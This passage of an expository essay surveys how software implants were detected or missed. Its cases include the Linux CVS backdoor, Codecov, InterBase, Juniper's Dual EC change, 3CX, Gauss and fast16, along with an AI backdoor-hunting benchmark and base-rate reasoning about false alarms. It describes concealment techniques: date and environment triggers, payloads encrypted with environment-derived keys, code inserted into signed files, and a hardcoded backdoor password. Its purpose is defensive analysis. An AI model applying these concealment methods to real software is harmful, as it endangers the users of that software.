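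Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel project, said the two lines could not have reached an official release from the CVS copy, because he accepted changes only through BitKeeper or as emailed patches. McVoy thought they could have got in indirectly, if a developer working from the CVS copy had included them in a patch without noticing. Torvalds said that any patch to a core file would be read through and need an explanation, but nobody can know whether he would have spotted the missing equals sign.

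Theodore Ts'o, also a kernel developer, described an attack that BitMover's comparison could not have caught. An attacker could forge an email from a trusted developer containing a supposed bug fix, with a harmful change hidden among plausible ones. If Torvalds accepted the patch, the conversion program would copy the backdoor to CVS and add a proper link, and every checksum would match. Twenty years later, Jia Tan did something similar to xz without having to forge anyone's address.

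### One customer's checksum

Codecov sells a service that measures how much of a program its tests exercise. Customers' build machines automatically downloaded and ran a script, the Bash Uploader, to send in their results. Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)* (2021) explains that an attacker found a storage key in a software image the company had published and used it to change the script that customers downloaded, but not its source on GitHub.

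Codecov's *Bash Uploader Security Update* (2021) reproduces the single line of code the attacker needed. It sent the attacker's server the addresses of the customer's repositories and all the build machine's environment variables, which often contain passwords and keys. The line's options set the download tool to print nothing and to give up after half a second, so the build would hardly have slowed down even if the attacker's server had been unreachable.

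CISA's *Codecov Releases Security Update* (2021), an alert from the US government's cybersecurity agency, dates the first alteration of Codecov's script to 31 January 2021. On 1 April a customer calculated the script's checksum, saw that it differed from the one on GitHub, and emailed Codecov. The implant had been in place for 60 days. Any customer could have found the mismatch on the first day, but few seem to have checked, and Codecov admitted that it had never properly documented how to do so. Even the developers of the Python language ran the script without checking it. Four weeks after the discovery, Stinner (2021) proposed in *Code coverage on the CI* that they start verifying the checksum.

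The check worked because the checksum and the script were stored in different places. The attacker could write to Codecov's storage but apparently not to its GitHub account. If Codecov had published the checksum next to the script, the attacker could have replaced both. Codecov has since set up an alert for any change to the stored script. Such an alert might have revealed the attack within minutes instead of 60 days.

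A checksum mismatch on its own doesn't reveal an attack, since a customer might reasonably have guessed that Codecov had released a new version and not yet updated the checksum. Finding the change was easy in this case because comparing two short text files shows exactly which line is new. With a compiled program, someone has to reverse engineer the difference.

### Rebuilding a program to check it

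The Codecov script did not need compiling, so the published file should have been identical to the source. Most programs are compiled, so comparing them with their source requires a reproducible build.

Developers make a build reproducible by removing anything that varies between runs. For example, they might set the date stored in the file to the date of the last source change instead of the current time. If several people then get identical files on unconnected machines, but the publisher distributed a different one, the publisher's build machine is the most likely source of the difference.

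Rebuilding a program from source and comparing the result with the released version is a good defence against an attack like the one on SolarWinds, whose repository was clean. To avoid detection, the attacker would have to break into every machine that anybody might use for a rebuild. But Orion's customers did not have its source, so only SolarWinds could have made the comparison, and it would have needed a build machine that the intruders had not reached. Builds can also differ for harmless reasons, and until developers have removed nearly all of these differences, a mismatch is weak evidence of tampering and people will learn to ignore it.

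An integrity check compares software with a trusted original, so it fails when that original is malicious. Rebuilding xz from its release archive, for example, would have reproduced the implant.

### A password in the source

InterBase was a Borland database program whose customers included Boeing, Nokia and the Boston Stock Exchange. Anyone who logged in with the user name "politically" and the password "correct" could read and change everything in the database. If the server program was running as root, they could also take over the whole machine. CERT Coordination Center's *Borland/Inprise Interbase SQL database server contains backdoor superuser account with known password* (2001) found that Borland's own programmers had written the account into the source. Every legitimate copy therefore contained it, and no checksum or rebuild would have shown anything wrong.

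Borland's programmers seem to have added the back door to solve a design problem. Schneier (2001), in *Back Door Security Threat in Interbase Teaches Broader Lessons*, explains that when Borland added passwords to InterBase, it stored them in an InterBase database. The program therefore had to check a user's password before it could open the database that held the passwords. The programmers got around this with an account that was always valid. InterBase's founder, who had left before Borland added the account, told Shankland (2001), in *Security hole found in Borland database*, that the addition was innocent.

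Borland released the source in July 2000. Five months later, on 18 December, a programmer on Firebird, a project based on that source, found the account. The public learned of it in January 2001. Most reports say Borland added the account in 1994, about six years before it was found, but FreeBSD (2001) dates it to 1992, which would make it eight years. Until the July release, few people outside Borland could have read the source.

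Source review succeeded here, but the account was easy to find because nobody had disguised it. The user name and password were in plain English in a file called pwd.h, and the account's internal name, LOCKSMITH, appeared in ten source files. If Borland's programmers meant no harm, they had no reason to hide the account from reviewers, as someone planting a malicious implant would. Schneier was cautious about crediting open source, because publishing the source would have made matters worse if a criminal had been the first to notice the account.

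### Juniper's changed constant

On 17 December 2015, Juniper Networks' chief information officer reported in *Important Announcement about ScreenOS* that "a recent internal code review" had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS (Worrall, 2015). ScreenOS is the operating system of Juniper's NetScreen devices, which companies use as firewalls and to run virtual private networks (VPNs), encrypted connections over the internet.

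Juniper's ScreenOS contained two implants. Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018) reconstructed their history in *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* by reverse engineering dozens of ScreenOS versions. One implant let an eavesdropper decrypt VPN connections. It had appeared by August 2012, at least three years and four months before the announcement in December 2015. The other was a fixed password that gave anyone who knew it control of the device. It first appeared in a release of April 2013, at least two years and eight months before the announcement. Someone had changed Juniper's own source code, and Juniper then built and distributed the altered versions as official releases.

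The decryption implant was little more than a new number. VPNs need random numbers to make their keys, and ScreenOS produced them with a generator called Dual EC. The generator keeps a secret number $s$, its state, and uses two public points, $P$ and $Q$, on an elliptic curve, a mathematical curve whose points can be multiplied by whole numbers. Multiplying is quick, but there is no publicly known practical way to work back from the result to the number. At each step the generator calculates

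$$r_1 = x(s_1 Q), \qquad s_2 = x(s_1 P)$$

where $x$ means the first coordinate of a point. Most of $r_1$ becomes output, and $s_2$ becomes the next state.

Suppose that somebody knows a number $d$ for which $P = dQ$. They can reconstruct the point $s_1 Q$ from the output and multiply it by $d$:

$$d(s_1 Q) = s_1(dQ) = s_1 P.$$

The first coordinate of this point is $s_2$, the generator's next state, so anyone who computes it can predict everything the generator will produce. ScreenOS revealed 30 of the 32 bytes of $r_1$, which left $2^{16}$, or 65,536, possibilities for the rest. Finding $d$ from $P$ and $Q$ is infeasible, but a person who picks $Q$ can pick it so that they already know $d$. The intruder replaced Juniper's $Q$ with another one, presumably chosen this way. They also changed the stored answer to a self-test, which was itself an integrity check, so that the generator would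 still pass.

Testing the devices' output could not have revealed this implant because, according to Checkoway and colleagues, the numbers looked just as random as before to anyone who didn't know $d$. An eavesdropper could use the implant by recording traffic, without contacting the device, so there would be no odd login or connection to notice either. Only reading the code or comparing it with an earlier version could have revealed the implant.

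That makes Juniper's review the best example of review catching a malicious implant, but Juniper has not said what prompted it. Checkoway and colleagues report that the company refused to give details even when a congressional committee held a hearing. The reviewers may have been reading the code routinely, or they may have had a tip or a sign of intrusion that showed them where to look.

Juniper's announcement did not explain the flaws, but it came with repaired versions of ScreenOS, which helped outsiders identify them within days. Wong describes in *Juniper's backdoor* how researchers compared the text in the vulnerable and repaired files, saw that a few numbers had changed, and noticed that these sat next to the parameters of a standard elliptic curve. As with the Linux backdoor, a comparison narrowed the search to a few lines before anyone had to understand them.

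Reading the same part of ScreenOS without such a comparison was much harder. Juniper had said in 2013 that its use of Dual EC was safe because a second generator scrambled the output, but the second generator never ran. Its code was in a loop that continued only while a counter was at most 31, and a subroutine called just before the loop set that counter to 32. Several experienced researchers who knew that the routine probably contained a bug missed it before one of them, Willem Pinckaers, found it. The accredited laboratory that certified ScreenOS had missed it too. As far as anyone knows, Juniper's engineers made this mistake in 2008, so it survived for seven years without any attempt to hide it.

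### How much do reviewers find?

Experiments can measure how often code review misses implants, if the researchers know in advance what is in the code. Successful cases can't show this because nobody counts the implants that reviewers read and passed.

In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 developers to review by hand a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities of three common kinds. No developer found all seven, and those with more experience were not necessarily more accurate. Developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, which suggests that some were simply quicker to call code suspicious.

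A later online experiment with 146 participants, most of them software developers, tested whether it helps to tell reviewers what to look for. The code they reviewed failed to check data coming from outside the program. Prompting helped, but many participants still missed the flaw when the code did not suggest a familiar kind of attack. This fits the Linux case, where people quickly recognised the backdoor once McVoy had told them the lines were unauthorised.

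Reviewers of real projects consider security. Charoenwet, Thongtanunam and colleagues (2023) examined 135,560 review comments from OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, and the programming language PHP. Reviewers had raised concerns about 35 of 40 categories of coding weakness. The comments record what reviewers noticed, so they can't show how much reviewers missed.

All this research concerns accidental flaws, and it isn't clear how well it applies to implants. Some implants may be easier to find, because a secret password is something in the code that shouldn't be there, while a missing check leaves nothing to notice. But an attacker can study how reviewers work and then write code that will satisfy them. The Linux attacker, for example, chose a mistake that programmers often make.

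### AI systems as reverse engineers

AI systems could make it practical to inspect far more code than people have time for. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) tested this in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra* with a benchmark called BinaryAudit. They added backdoors by hand to open-source network programs, including a web server and an SSH server. They compiled the programs and gave AI agents only the binaries, along with free reverse engineering tools such as Ghidra. In most tasks an agent had to decide whether the program contained a backdoor and give the address of the function responsible, so correctly guessing "yes" was not enough.

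The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of the tasks, compared with 44% for Gemini 3 Pro and 37% for Claude Opus 4.5. The backdoors were fairly easy, and a skilled human reverse engineer could have spotted them. On clean programs, the models reported a nonexistent problem 28% of the time.

In one successful test, Claude Opus 4.5 found a backdoor without reading all the code. The experimenters had modified a web server to run any command sent in a secret header, a labelled line at the start of a web request. The model first searched the files for suspicious words and found nothing. It then listed the outside functions that each library used and found that one library could run shell commands. It traced this ability to a function called li_check_debug_header, decompiled it and understood the backdoor, all within five minutes. However, the function's name had survived compilation, and the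 model took it as further evidence of a backdoor. A careful attacker would have chosen a less revealing name.

Claude Opus 4.6 missed a backdoor that the experimenters called embarrassingly obvious. They had added seven lines to dnsmasq, a program that assigns network addresses, so that it would run commands hidden in a network message. The model found the right function and identified that it ran a shell command, but classified this as a legitimate dnsmasq feature without checking where the command came from. Claude Code had made the same kind of mistake when it reported to McMahon that the processes filling his laptop were not malware.

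The benchmark's results page, Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, includes later models. Gemini 3.1 Pro found 49% of the backdoors and raised false alarms on 17% of the clean programs. GPT-5.2-Codex found 46% at its highest reasoning setting, with no false alarms. It found only 9% at its ordinary setting, so the amount of reasoning can matter more than the choice of model. GPT-5.4 is newer but found only 18% at its highest setting.

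The false positive rate of zero is encouraging, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks. Even if every one had been a clean program, a model that wrongly flags 9% of clean programs would have had about a one in twenty chance of raising no false alarms. Grabowski and colleagues think a practical detector needs a false positive rate below 0.001%. FireEye had about 4,000 executable files to search when it took Orion apart. At Gemini 3.1 Pro's rates, an agent would have flagged about 680 harmless files and had a roughly even chance of flagging the infected one. This might still have saved FireEye some work, but a company with no reason to suspect Orion would probably have given up on checking the flagged files.

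These models date from early 2026 or before, so the scores may already understate what AI systems can do. Grabowski and colleagues note that a year earlier, models could not reliably operate Ghidra. The benchmark left out programs written in Go because the free tools handled them badly.

Tests on real files are less controlled. VirusTotal (2025), a service that scans files with many antivirus products, compared those products with its own AI tool, Code Insight. Together, the antivirus products flagged 67 files in the set, while Code Insight flagged 164. Manual review found that 30 of the 67 were false alarms from Microsoft's product, so conventional scanners raise false alarms too. Nobody knows how many malicious files both methods missed, and VirusTotal was judging its own tool.

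BinaryAudit's agents usually had to search a program without a clean version to compare it with. A clean version makes the search much smaller in both programs and neural networks. GPT5 had an earlier release for comparison when it correctly judged the compromised xz library to be malicious.

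## When does anomaly detection fail?

False alarms are a problem in runtime monitoring, as they are for tools that search binaries. If most alerts have harmless causes, people may dismiss the one that an implant sets off. A dormant implant may not set off any alert.

### A thousand false alarms for each true one

Suppose one event in a million on a company's computers is malicious. The company's detector catches 99% of malicious events and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless ones. On average, a million events will produce 0.99 true alarms and about 1,000 false ones. An analyst who opens an alarm at random has roughly a one in a thousand chance of finding an attack.

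Most people would guess that such an accurate detector is usually right when it raises an alarm. Statisticians call this mistake the base-rate fallacy, because it ignores the base rate, which here is how common malicious events are to begin with. If $p$ is the base rate, $d$ the share of malicious events that the detector catches and $f$ its false positive rate, Bayes' theorem gives the chance that an alarm is real:

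$$P(\text{malicious} \mid \text{alarm}) = \frac{pd}{pd + (1-p)f}$$

When malicious events are rare, this works out to about $f/(pd)$ false alarms for each true one. A perfect detection rate would hardly help in the example, since it would only reduce the number of false alarms per true one from 1,010 to 1,000. Lowering the false positive rate helps far more:

| False positive rate | False alarms per million events | Share of alarms that are real |
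|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 1,000 | 0.1% |
| 0.01% | 100 | 1% |
| 0.001% | 10 | 9% |
| 0.0001% | 1 | 50% |

Axelsson applied this reasoning to computer security in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (1999) and expanded it in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000). He imagined an office with a couple of dozen users, where each day brings a million log records and two attempted intrusions. An intrusion would affect about ten records, so he treated the day's log as 100,000 events, two of them hostile. This base rate is 20 times higher than the one above, but a detector that wrongly flagged one harmless event in 1,000 would still raise about 100 false alarms a day and at most two true ones.

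Axelsson concluded that the office needed a false positive rate of about one in 100,000 (0.001%). At that rate, the office would get one false alarm a day, and if the detector caught 70% of intrusions, 58% of its alarms would be real. Grabowski and colleagues arrived at the same figure for tools that look for backdoors in binaries.

His standard relied on staff continuing to respond even if half the alarms were false. Nobody had tested this in computer security, but studies of operators in places such as power stations and paper mills suggested that most would have stopped trusting the detector by that point.

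Axelsson also looked at published tests of real detectors, and the anomaly detectors all had false positive rates at least ten times higher than he allowed. Some detectors that looked for known patterns of attack came close to his standard, but in the largest test, detection rates fell sharply when the attacks were new. This is a serious weakness for finding implants, because a newly written implant may not match any known pattern.

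Axelsson's figures describe a small Unix office in the 1990s, and he acknowledged that the probabilities were subjective. The figures also depend on what counts as an event. Checking each computer once a day would produce a few dozen daily events instead of 100,000, and so fewer chances of a false alarm. But implants in trusted software are presumably much rarer than attempted intrusions, so a company looking for them faces an even lower base rate than he assumed.

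One way to reduce false alarms is to require two different signs. Suppose the company in the first example adds a second detector that is just as accurate and whose mistakes are independent of the first one's. Only about one harmless event in a million will set off both, so about half of the double alarms will be real. In practice, the same unusual but harmless program may well set off both detectors, in which case double alarms will be less reliable.

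### Customers who overruled the alarm

In March 2023, customers of 3CX dismissed genuine warnings of an implant as false alarms. 3CX sells internet phone software to more than 600,000 customers. MITRE's *3CX Supply Chain Attack* (2025) traces the attack to an employee who had installed a tampered copy of X_Trader, a discontinued financial trading program. This gave the intruders, whom security companies linked to North Korea, a way to reach the machines that built 3CX's Windows and Mac apps. MITRE calls it the first publicly reported case of one supply chain attack leading to another.

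SentinelOne's security software blocked the infected installers because of how they behaved. On 22 March a customer asked on 3CX's forum whether other companies' products were raising the same alert. The alert listed shellcode, a kind of machine code that intruders often use, and the injection of code into another program's memory.

Creative Collaboration's *3CX knew its app was flagged as malicious* (2023) follows the discussion over the next week. Other customers reported the same warning, soon decided that SentinelOne's product was at fault, and set up exceptions to let the app run. On 28 March one customer wrote that they had also added an exception but did "not like defaulting to trust". 3CX's support staff first replied a few minutes later, advising customers to contact SentinelOne. When a customer suggested that 3CX should do this itself, the support representative answered that there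 were hundreds if not thousands of antivirus products, and that SentinelOne might be blocking some function of Electron, the framework 3CX had used for the app.

3CX's chief executive, Nick Galea, said in CyberScoop's *‘They outsmarted us.’ 3CX CEO acknowledges mistakes* that security products flagged the company's app quite often, so "we didn't take it that seriously." 3CX did check the app on VirusTotal, where no antivirus product flagged it. It checked again a few days later and got the same result, according to Vumetric's *3CX thought supply chain attack was a false positive* (2023).

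CrowdStrike reported the attack publicly on 29 March. It reverse engineered the installer and confirmed that the file was malicious. The implant's traffic format and encryption key matched those in a campaign from earlier that month, which CrowdStrike had already attributed to a North Korean group.

3CX and its customers reasonably began by suspecting a false positive, since earlier alerts about the app had apparently been harmless. They then found that other customers had the same alert, but this didn't show whether it was false, because a fault in SentinelOne's product would also have affected all of them. An alert from another company's product would have been stronger evidence, as the first customer seems to have realised. TechTarget reports that products from Sophos and ESET also flagged the app, though it isn't clear how early.

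The VirusTotal result was weak evidence because a new implant could easily have passed the same test. Antivirus products are best at recognising malware that someone has already identified, while SentinelOne's had reacted to what the app did when it ran. Rescanning the app a few days later could help only if the antivirus companies had learned something in the meantime. 3CX's own scans had also missed the implant, and Apple had checked the Mac installer for malware and approved it. All these checks probably had the same weakness, so their clean results were not independent confirmation.

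The base-rate argument shows that most alarms are false, but that alone doesn't justify ignoring one. The decision also depends on how much work an investigation takes and how much harm would follow if the alarm is real. *Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* proposes rules for how long a defender should wait before responding, because acting on every signal is expensive and ignoring them all makes the detector useless. At 3CX, the effort of asking SentinelOne which action had triggered the alert would have been very small compared with the risk to its customers.

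Erbacher (2022) argues in *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity* that false positives deserve the same close analysis as true positives. Such an analysis would have helped in the 3CX case, where people dismissed SentinelOne's alerts without finding the supposed fault in its product. Investigators likewise dismissed earlier signs of the SolarWinds implant after settling on an explanation they hadn't confirmed.

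### Why a broken rule is easier to act on

The alert FireEye's analyst received was also of a type that is usually harmless, but the analyst could resolve it by checking whether the employee had registered the phone. If not, someone else had, which almost never has an innocent explanation.

Suppose such a question takes five minutes, while reverse engineering an unfamiliar program takes a day. With 1,010 false alarms for each true one, an analyst would need about 84 hours to find an attack by asking questions, but about four working years by reverse engineering, even though the false positive rate is the same. A broken rule is easier to act on largely because the analyst already knows what would make the event innocent and can quickly check for it.

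A statistical anomaly doesn't show the analyst what to check. *Outside the Closed World* (Sommer and Paxson, 2010) argues that machine learning had succeeded less in intrusion detection than in other fields partly because it is better at recognising things that resemble its training examples than at finding something new. Ordinary network traffic also varies so much that unusual traffic is often harmless. Even a correct detection leaves what the paper calls a "semantic gap" between the result and what it means for the people running the network. If a server sends three times as much data as usual one night, for example, the cause may be a backup, a new customer or data theft.

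Several of the discoveries described earlier involved broken rules. Every change in the public copy of the Linux source was supposed to have a counterpart in BitKeeper, and the backdoor had none. BackupAgent, a retired program, should not have been running on the Kaspersky employees' iPhones. By contrast, the half-second delay caused by xz and the crashes caused by Stuxnet had many possible explanations, so Freund and Ulasen had to do a lot of work before they knew they were dealing with malware.

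The SentinelOne alert was somewhere in between. Most programs have no reason to inject code into another program, but a few legitimate ones do, and 3CX's customers could easily believe that an internet phone app was one of them.

Rules have their own weaknesses. Somebody has to think of each rule in advance, and an intruder may be able to comply with it, as the SolarWinds intruders could by calculating valid login codes. A badly chosen rule also causes false alarms. In his first paper, Axelsson warned designers against any rule with even a remote chance of reacting to harmless activity.

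### Triggers by date, environment and secret key

An anomaly detector can work perfectly and still miss an implant that has not been triggered. The kind of trigger determines how long the implant can stay dormant and whether a tester can activate it.

A date trigger keeps an implant inactive until a set time. Cisco Talos' *3CX softphone supply chain compromise* describes a seven-day sleep before the Windows version looked for further instructions, while MITRE describes a random date between one and four weeks ahead. The two accounts may refer to different parts or versions of the malware. Huntress' *3CX VoIP software compromise supply chain threats* suggests that the delay may explain why some 3CX users had not yet seen any malicious activity. The SolarWinds implant also waited for up to two weeks.

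SentinelOne's product raised its alerts before the seven days had passed. It reacted to shellcode, and Huntress found that the part of the implant that slept was inside that shellcode. The product therefore detected the code that loaded the implant while the rest was still dormant. Customers who made an exception for the app gave the implant time to reach its activation date.

Testers can look for date triggers by moving a computer's clock forward. Ten years has only about 3,650 days, so a program could try them all. But a careful attacker might make the implant also check the time with an outside server.

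An environment trigger makes the implant act only on certain machines. Stuxnet's payload needed specific industrial controllers, and the SolarWinds implant stopped if the computer was not part of a Windows domain. A tester who doesn't know the condition can't easily reproduce it, because computers can differ in so many ways. An analyst who has the code can often read the condition and build a machine that satisfies it.

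Some implants respond only to a secret key, as xz's did to messages signed with one private key. Ordinary use can set off an implant triggered by a date or a particular environment, but it won't set off one that needs a secret key, because nobody will enter a long random key by chance.

### The odds of guessing a secret

It is easy to calculate how little random testing helps against a secret key. A secret of $k$ bits has $2^k$ possible values. If the attacker picked one at random, a single random test finds it with probability $1/2^k$ and misses it with probability $1 - 1/2^k$. For $n$ independent tests, the chance that at least one succeeds is

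$$1 - \left(1 - \frac{1}{2^k}\right)^n \approx \frac{n}{2^k}$$

The approximation holds while $n$ is much smaller than $2^k$. If the tester never tries the same value twice, the chance is exactly $n/2^k$.

Suppose that somebody runs a trillion tests on a program with a 64-bit trigger:

$$\frac{10^{12}}{2^{64}} \approx \frac{10^{12}}{1.8 \times 10^{19}} \approx 5.4 \times 10^{-8}$$

The trillion tests would have about one chance in 18 million of finding the trigger, and would take nearly 12 days at a million tests a second. The tester would need to continue at that rate for about 292,000 years to have an even chance of finding it.

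Shorter triggers are much easier to find. The password in the sudo example, "let_me_in", has nine characters. If the tester knew that each one was a lower-case letter or an underscore, there would be about 7.6 trillion possibilities ($27^9$), and a trillion different guesses would have a 13% chance of finding it. A tester who tried common phrases first would probably find it almost at once.

The estimate also assumes that a wrong guess gives no information. Imagine a program that compares an eight-byte secret with the input one byte at a time and stops at the first difference. If the tester can observe how far the comparison gets, they can find each byte separately, with at most 256 guesses for each. That makes 2,048 guesses in total, instead of up to $2^{64}$. (A neural network's trigger need not be exact, which also changes the odds.)

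Someone who can read the code can also copy out the secret if the program stores it. If the program stores only a hash of the secret, they may not be able to recover it, but they can still see the check and read the payload behind it. An attacker can prevent them from reading the payload by encrypting it and leaving the key out of the program.

### Gauss and its locked payload

In August 2012, Kaspersky announced that it had discovered Gauss, a set of espionage tools that stole browser passwords, bank login details and information about infected computers. Kaspersky (2012) had recorded more than 2,500 infections since late May, most of them in the Middle East. One part of Gauss, called Godel, contained a payload that Kaspersky could not decrypt.

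Gauss tried to construct the key to its encrypted payload from the settings of each computer it infected, instead of carrying the key with it, as Kaspersky explained on Securelist. It combined text from PATH, a Windows setting that lists the folders where Windows looks for programs, with the name of a folder in the computer's Program Files directory. It then applied the MD5 hash function 10,000 times and used the result as a key. The payload would decrypt and run only on a computer with the right combination. On any other computer, neither the owner nor anyone who studied the malware there could read it.

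The key has 128 bits, according to Dark Reading's *Crypto Experts Called On To Crack Cyberspy Tool's Encryption* (2012), so a trillion random guesses would have a probability of about $3 \times 10^{-27}$ of finding it. An analyst would do better to guess the settings from which Gauss calculated the key. If the analyst listed a million plausible PATH entries and a million folder names, there would be a trillion pairs to test, each requiring 10,000 MD5 calculations. A computer that performed ten billion calculations a second would need just under 12 days to test them all. If Gauss had applied MD5 only once, the same search would take 100 seconds.

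A search for the key to Gauss's encrypted payload will fail if the right folder name is missing from the list, which is likely if the target used unusual software. *Researchers Seek Help Cracking Gauss Mystery Payload* (Zetter, 2012) reported that Kaspersky could not reproduce the key without knowing which systems Gauss was targeting or how their owners had set them up. In Securelist's *The Mystery of the Encrypted Gauss Payload*, Kaspersky acknowledged that it could not decrypt the payload and published what it knew so that cryptographers and mathematicians could help.

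Nobody appears to have announced a successful decryption since then. Someone may have decrypted the payload without saying so, but its purpose remains publicly unknown. Kaspersky pointed out that the payload was large enough to contain sabotage code like Stuxnet's, which is concerning but isn't evidence of what it did.

Quarkslab's *Bradley hash and decrypt Gauss* describes Bradley, a malware design that locked its payload in this way before Gauss did. Bradley had three encrypted layers. The first contained defences against antivirus software and calculated the key for the second. The second handled infection and calculated the key for the third, which contained the payloads. An analyst who couldn't open one layer therefore couldn't open the next. Gauss was simpler, since it seems to have decrypted all its locked parts together.

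Kaspersky's *Equation Group Questions and Answers* describes a related technique in GrayFish, malware from another espionage group. GrayFish calculated its decryption key from an ID number Windows had assigned to a folder on the victim's computer, so each infection worked on only one machine. Investigators who have that machine can look up the number and decrypt the next stage. In the Gauss case, they had thousands of infected machines but apparently not the one they needed for decryption.

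### What a dormant implant still exposes

Nobody could read Gauss's payload, which was dormant, but the rest of the malware was active and left traces, so it was not especially well hidden. Kaspersky found Gauss by looking for programs that resembled Flame, an espionage tool it already knew. Cryptography Engineering's *On Gauss* (2012) notes that Gauss also installed a new font, Palida Narrow, on every infected computer, for reasons Kaspersky could not explain. A user who knew about the font could have found it in the list of installed fonts.

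An implant that is only waiting for its trigger still uses some processor time to check for it, but an attacker who writes efficient code can make this almost undetectable. Gauss's check was fairly slow. On a computer with 20 PATH entries and 50 program folders, testing every pair would take ten million hash calculations, or perhaps a second or two. Comparing an input with one stored number takes a tiny fraction of a microsecond, which nobody would notice. The slow part of the xz backdoor was its search for function names, not its check for the attacker's message.

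The implant also takes up space and usually makes a file larger, as Thompson's did. An encrypted payload may stand out because it looks like random data, but compressed pictures, installers and xz's legitimate test files look random too. Someone who finds an encrypted block has reason to ask what it is for, but may not be able to find out.

If a clean copy of a file exists, comparing the file with it is more reliable than looking for suspicious code. The attackers who compromised 3CX hid the main part of the Windows implant in ffmpeg.dll, a library that the app used for audio and video. MITRE reports that they used SigFlip, a tool that inserts code into a signed file without breaking the signature. This works because a Windows signature doesn't cover every byte of the file. A checksum of the whole altered file would have differed from that of a clean copy, whether or not the implant was inactive.

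Many implants also have to contact their operators for instructions. The Windows version of the 3CX implant downloaded icon files from a GitHub repository, where the attackers had added encrypted server addresses to the end of each file. A connection to GitHub seldom looks suspicious, but this repository was public, and Elastic found that the attackers created it on 8 December 2022, more than three months before the alerts. The Mac version contacted a server whose address was in the program, which is easier to spot once somebody has examined the code. An implant can avoid this exposure by waiting for its operator to make contact, as xz's did, or by activating on a preset date, which requires no message.

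A dormant implant may thus have no visible effect and still leave traces. Juniper's altered constant is probably the clearest known example. It caused no runtime anomaly even while an eavesdropper was using it, but comparing the software with an earlier version could have revealed it on the day of release.

Comparing software with a clean version can reveal an implant, but a clean version may not be available. Every legitimate copy of InterBase contained a secret account, so someone had to find it by reading the source code.

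An implant can also remove its traces. TriangleDB disappeared when an iPhone restarted, but traces of BackupAgent in the phone's backups still revealed the infection.

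## Which implants are missing from the record?

The implants described so far are all ones that somebody found. This sample can mislead because it leaves out undiscovered implants, a problem statisticians call survivorship bias. Anomalies exposed many of the best-known implants, but implants that cause no anomaly are the most likely to be missing from the record, so a new implant may still be unlikely to cause one.

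Suppose attackers have planted 200 implants (the numbers are invented). Forty are noisy, meaning they noticeably disturb the running system, and 160 are quiet. Monitoring finds half of the noisy ones, and source review finds 5% of the quiet ones.

| | Noisy | Quiet | All |
|---|---|---|---|
| Implants planted | 40 | 160 | 200 |
| Found by monitoring | 20 | 0 | 20 |
| Found by source review | 0 | 8 | 8 |
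| Still unknown | 20 | 152 | 172 |

The record contains 28 discoveries and credits anomalies with 20 of them. But those 20 are a small part of everything the attackers planted:

$$P(\text{anomaly} \mid \text{found}) = \frac{20}{28} \approx 71\%, \qquad P(\text{found through an anomaly}) = \frac{20}{200} = 10\%$$

A researcher cannot work out from the 28 cases alone what share of all implants anomalies exposed. If there were 1,600 quiet implants and review found 0.5% of them, it would still have found eight and the record would look the same, but anomalies would have exposed only 1.2% of all implants. To choose between these possibilities, a researcher needs to know how often each method misses an implant. The experiments on code review measured miss rates only for accidental flaws.

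### A search for an old scripting engine

*fast16* (2026), from the security company SentinelOne's research group SentinelLABS, describes a Windows implant that altered the results of engineering calculations. The implant went without a public report for more than 20 years. SentinelLABS dates its two main files to July and August 2005, based on timestamps left by the build tools.

The researchers found the implant by looking for early espionage tools, not by following up a crash or a strange result. They knew that several elaborate tools, including Flame, contained an engine for the scripting language Lua, and they wanted to find the earliest example. Compiled Lua code begins with the same four bytes, so they searched collections of malware from the mid-2000s for those bytes and other traces of the engine. One of the files they found, svcmgmt.exe, looked like an ordinary Windows service.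 It contained a Lua engine, some encrypted code and a file path left over from the build. The path included the name of the driver that did the sabotage, fast16, and led the researchers to it.

The driver looked for programs built with Intel's compiler, compared each one with 101 rules as Windows read it from disk, and changed the instructions that matched. Symantec's *Fast16*, published a month later, confirmed that the targets included LS-DYNA and AUTODYN, which engineers use to simulate crashes and explosions. The tampering began only when the simulated material passed a density of 30 grams per cubic centimetre. According to Symantec, uranium reaches that density only when explosives compress it in a nuclear weapon, so the sabotage would have stayed inactive during ordinary work.

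One of the implant's three routines lowered the calculated pressure along a straight line that would reach 1% of the true value at a density of 60. At a density $\rho$ between 30 and 60, the program would therefore report this fraction of the true pressure:

$$f(\rho) = 1 - 0.99 \times \frac{\rho - 30}{30}$$

At a density of 33, which Symantec tested, the fraction is about 90%, and the simulated material compressed more than it should have. Reversemode's *Inside Fast16's Physics Sabotage Engine* (2026) had already derived the general shape of this response from the code. It described LS-DYNA as a suspected target but had no solid evidence.

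The implant copied itself to nearby machines through shared network folders, so an engineer who doubted a result and repeated the calculation on another computer could well have got the same wrong answer. It also checked for security products and did not spread from machines that had them.

This doesn't prove that fast16 was quiet. Symantec found up to ten groups of rules for different builds of the simulation software, and the attackers seem to have added a group for an older build after one for a newer build. Symantec suggests that users may have noticed odd results and gone back to the older version, which the attackers then targeted too, but it calls this evidence anecdotal. If the guess is right, fast16 was like the 20 noisy implants that monitoring missed in the example, and users blamed the simulation software for the anomaly.

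Somebody uploaded svcmgmt.exe to VirusTotal almost a decade before SentinelLABS's report. Even in 2026, only one antivirus product there flagged it, with limited confidence. The implant was thus missing from the list of known attacks even though a copy was in a collection that security researchers use every day.

### How long before Stuxnet?

SentinelLABS says that fast16 predates Stuxnet by at least five years. Antiy's *A “Psychological Warfare” to Show Off Cyber Capabilities* objects that Stuxnet first attacked before the public learned of it in 2010. Citing newspaper investigations, Antiy says that an early version reached Natanz in 2007 and that the first known attack came in 2008. It accepts that fast16 came first but puts the gap at much less than five years. Antiy, a Chinese company, also accuses SentinelOne of timing its report to help the United States wage psychological warfare,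 but the objection about dates doesn't depend on that accusation.

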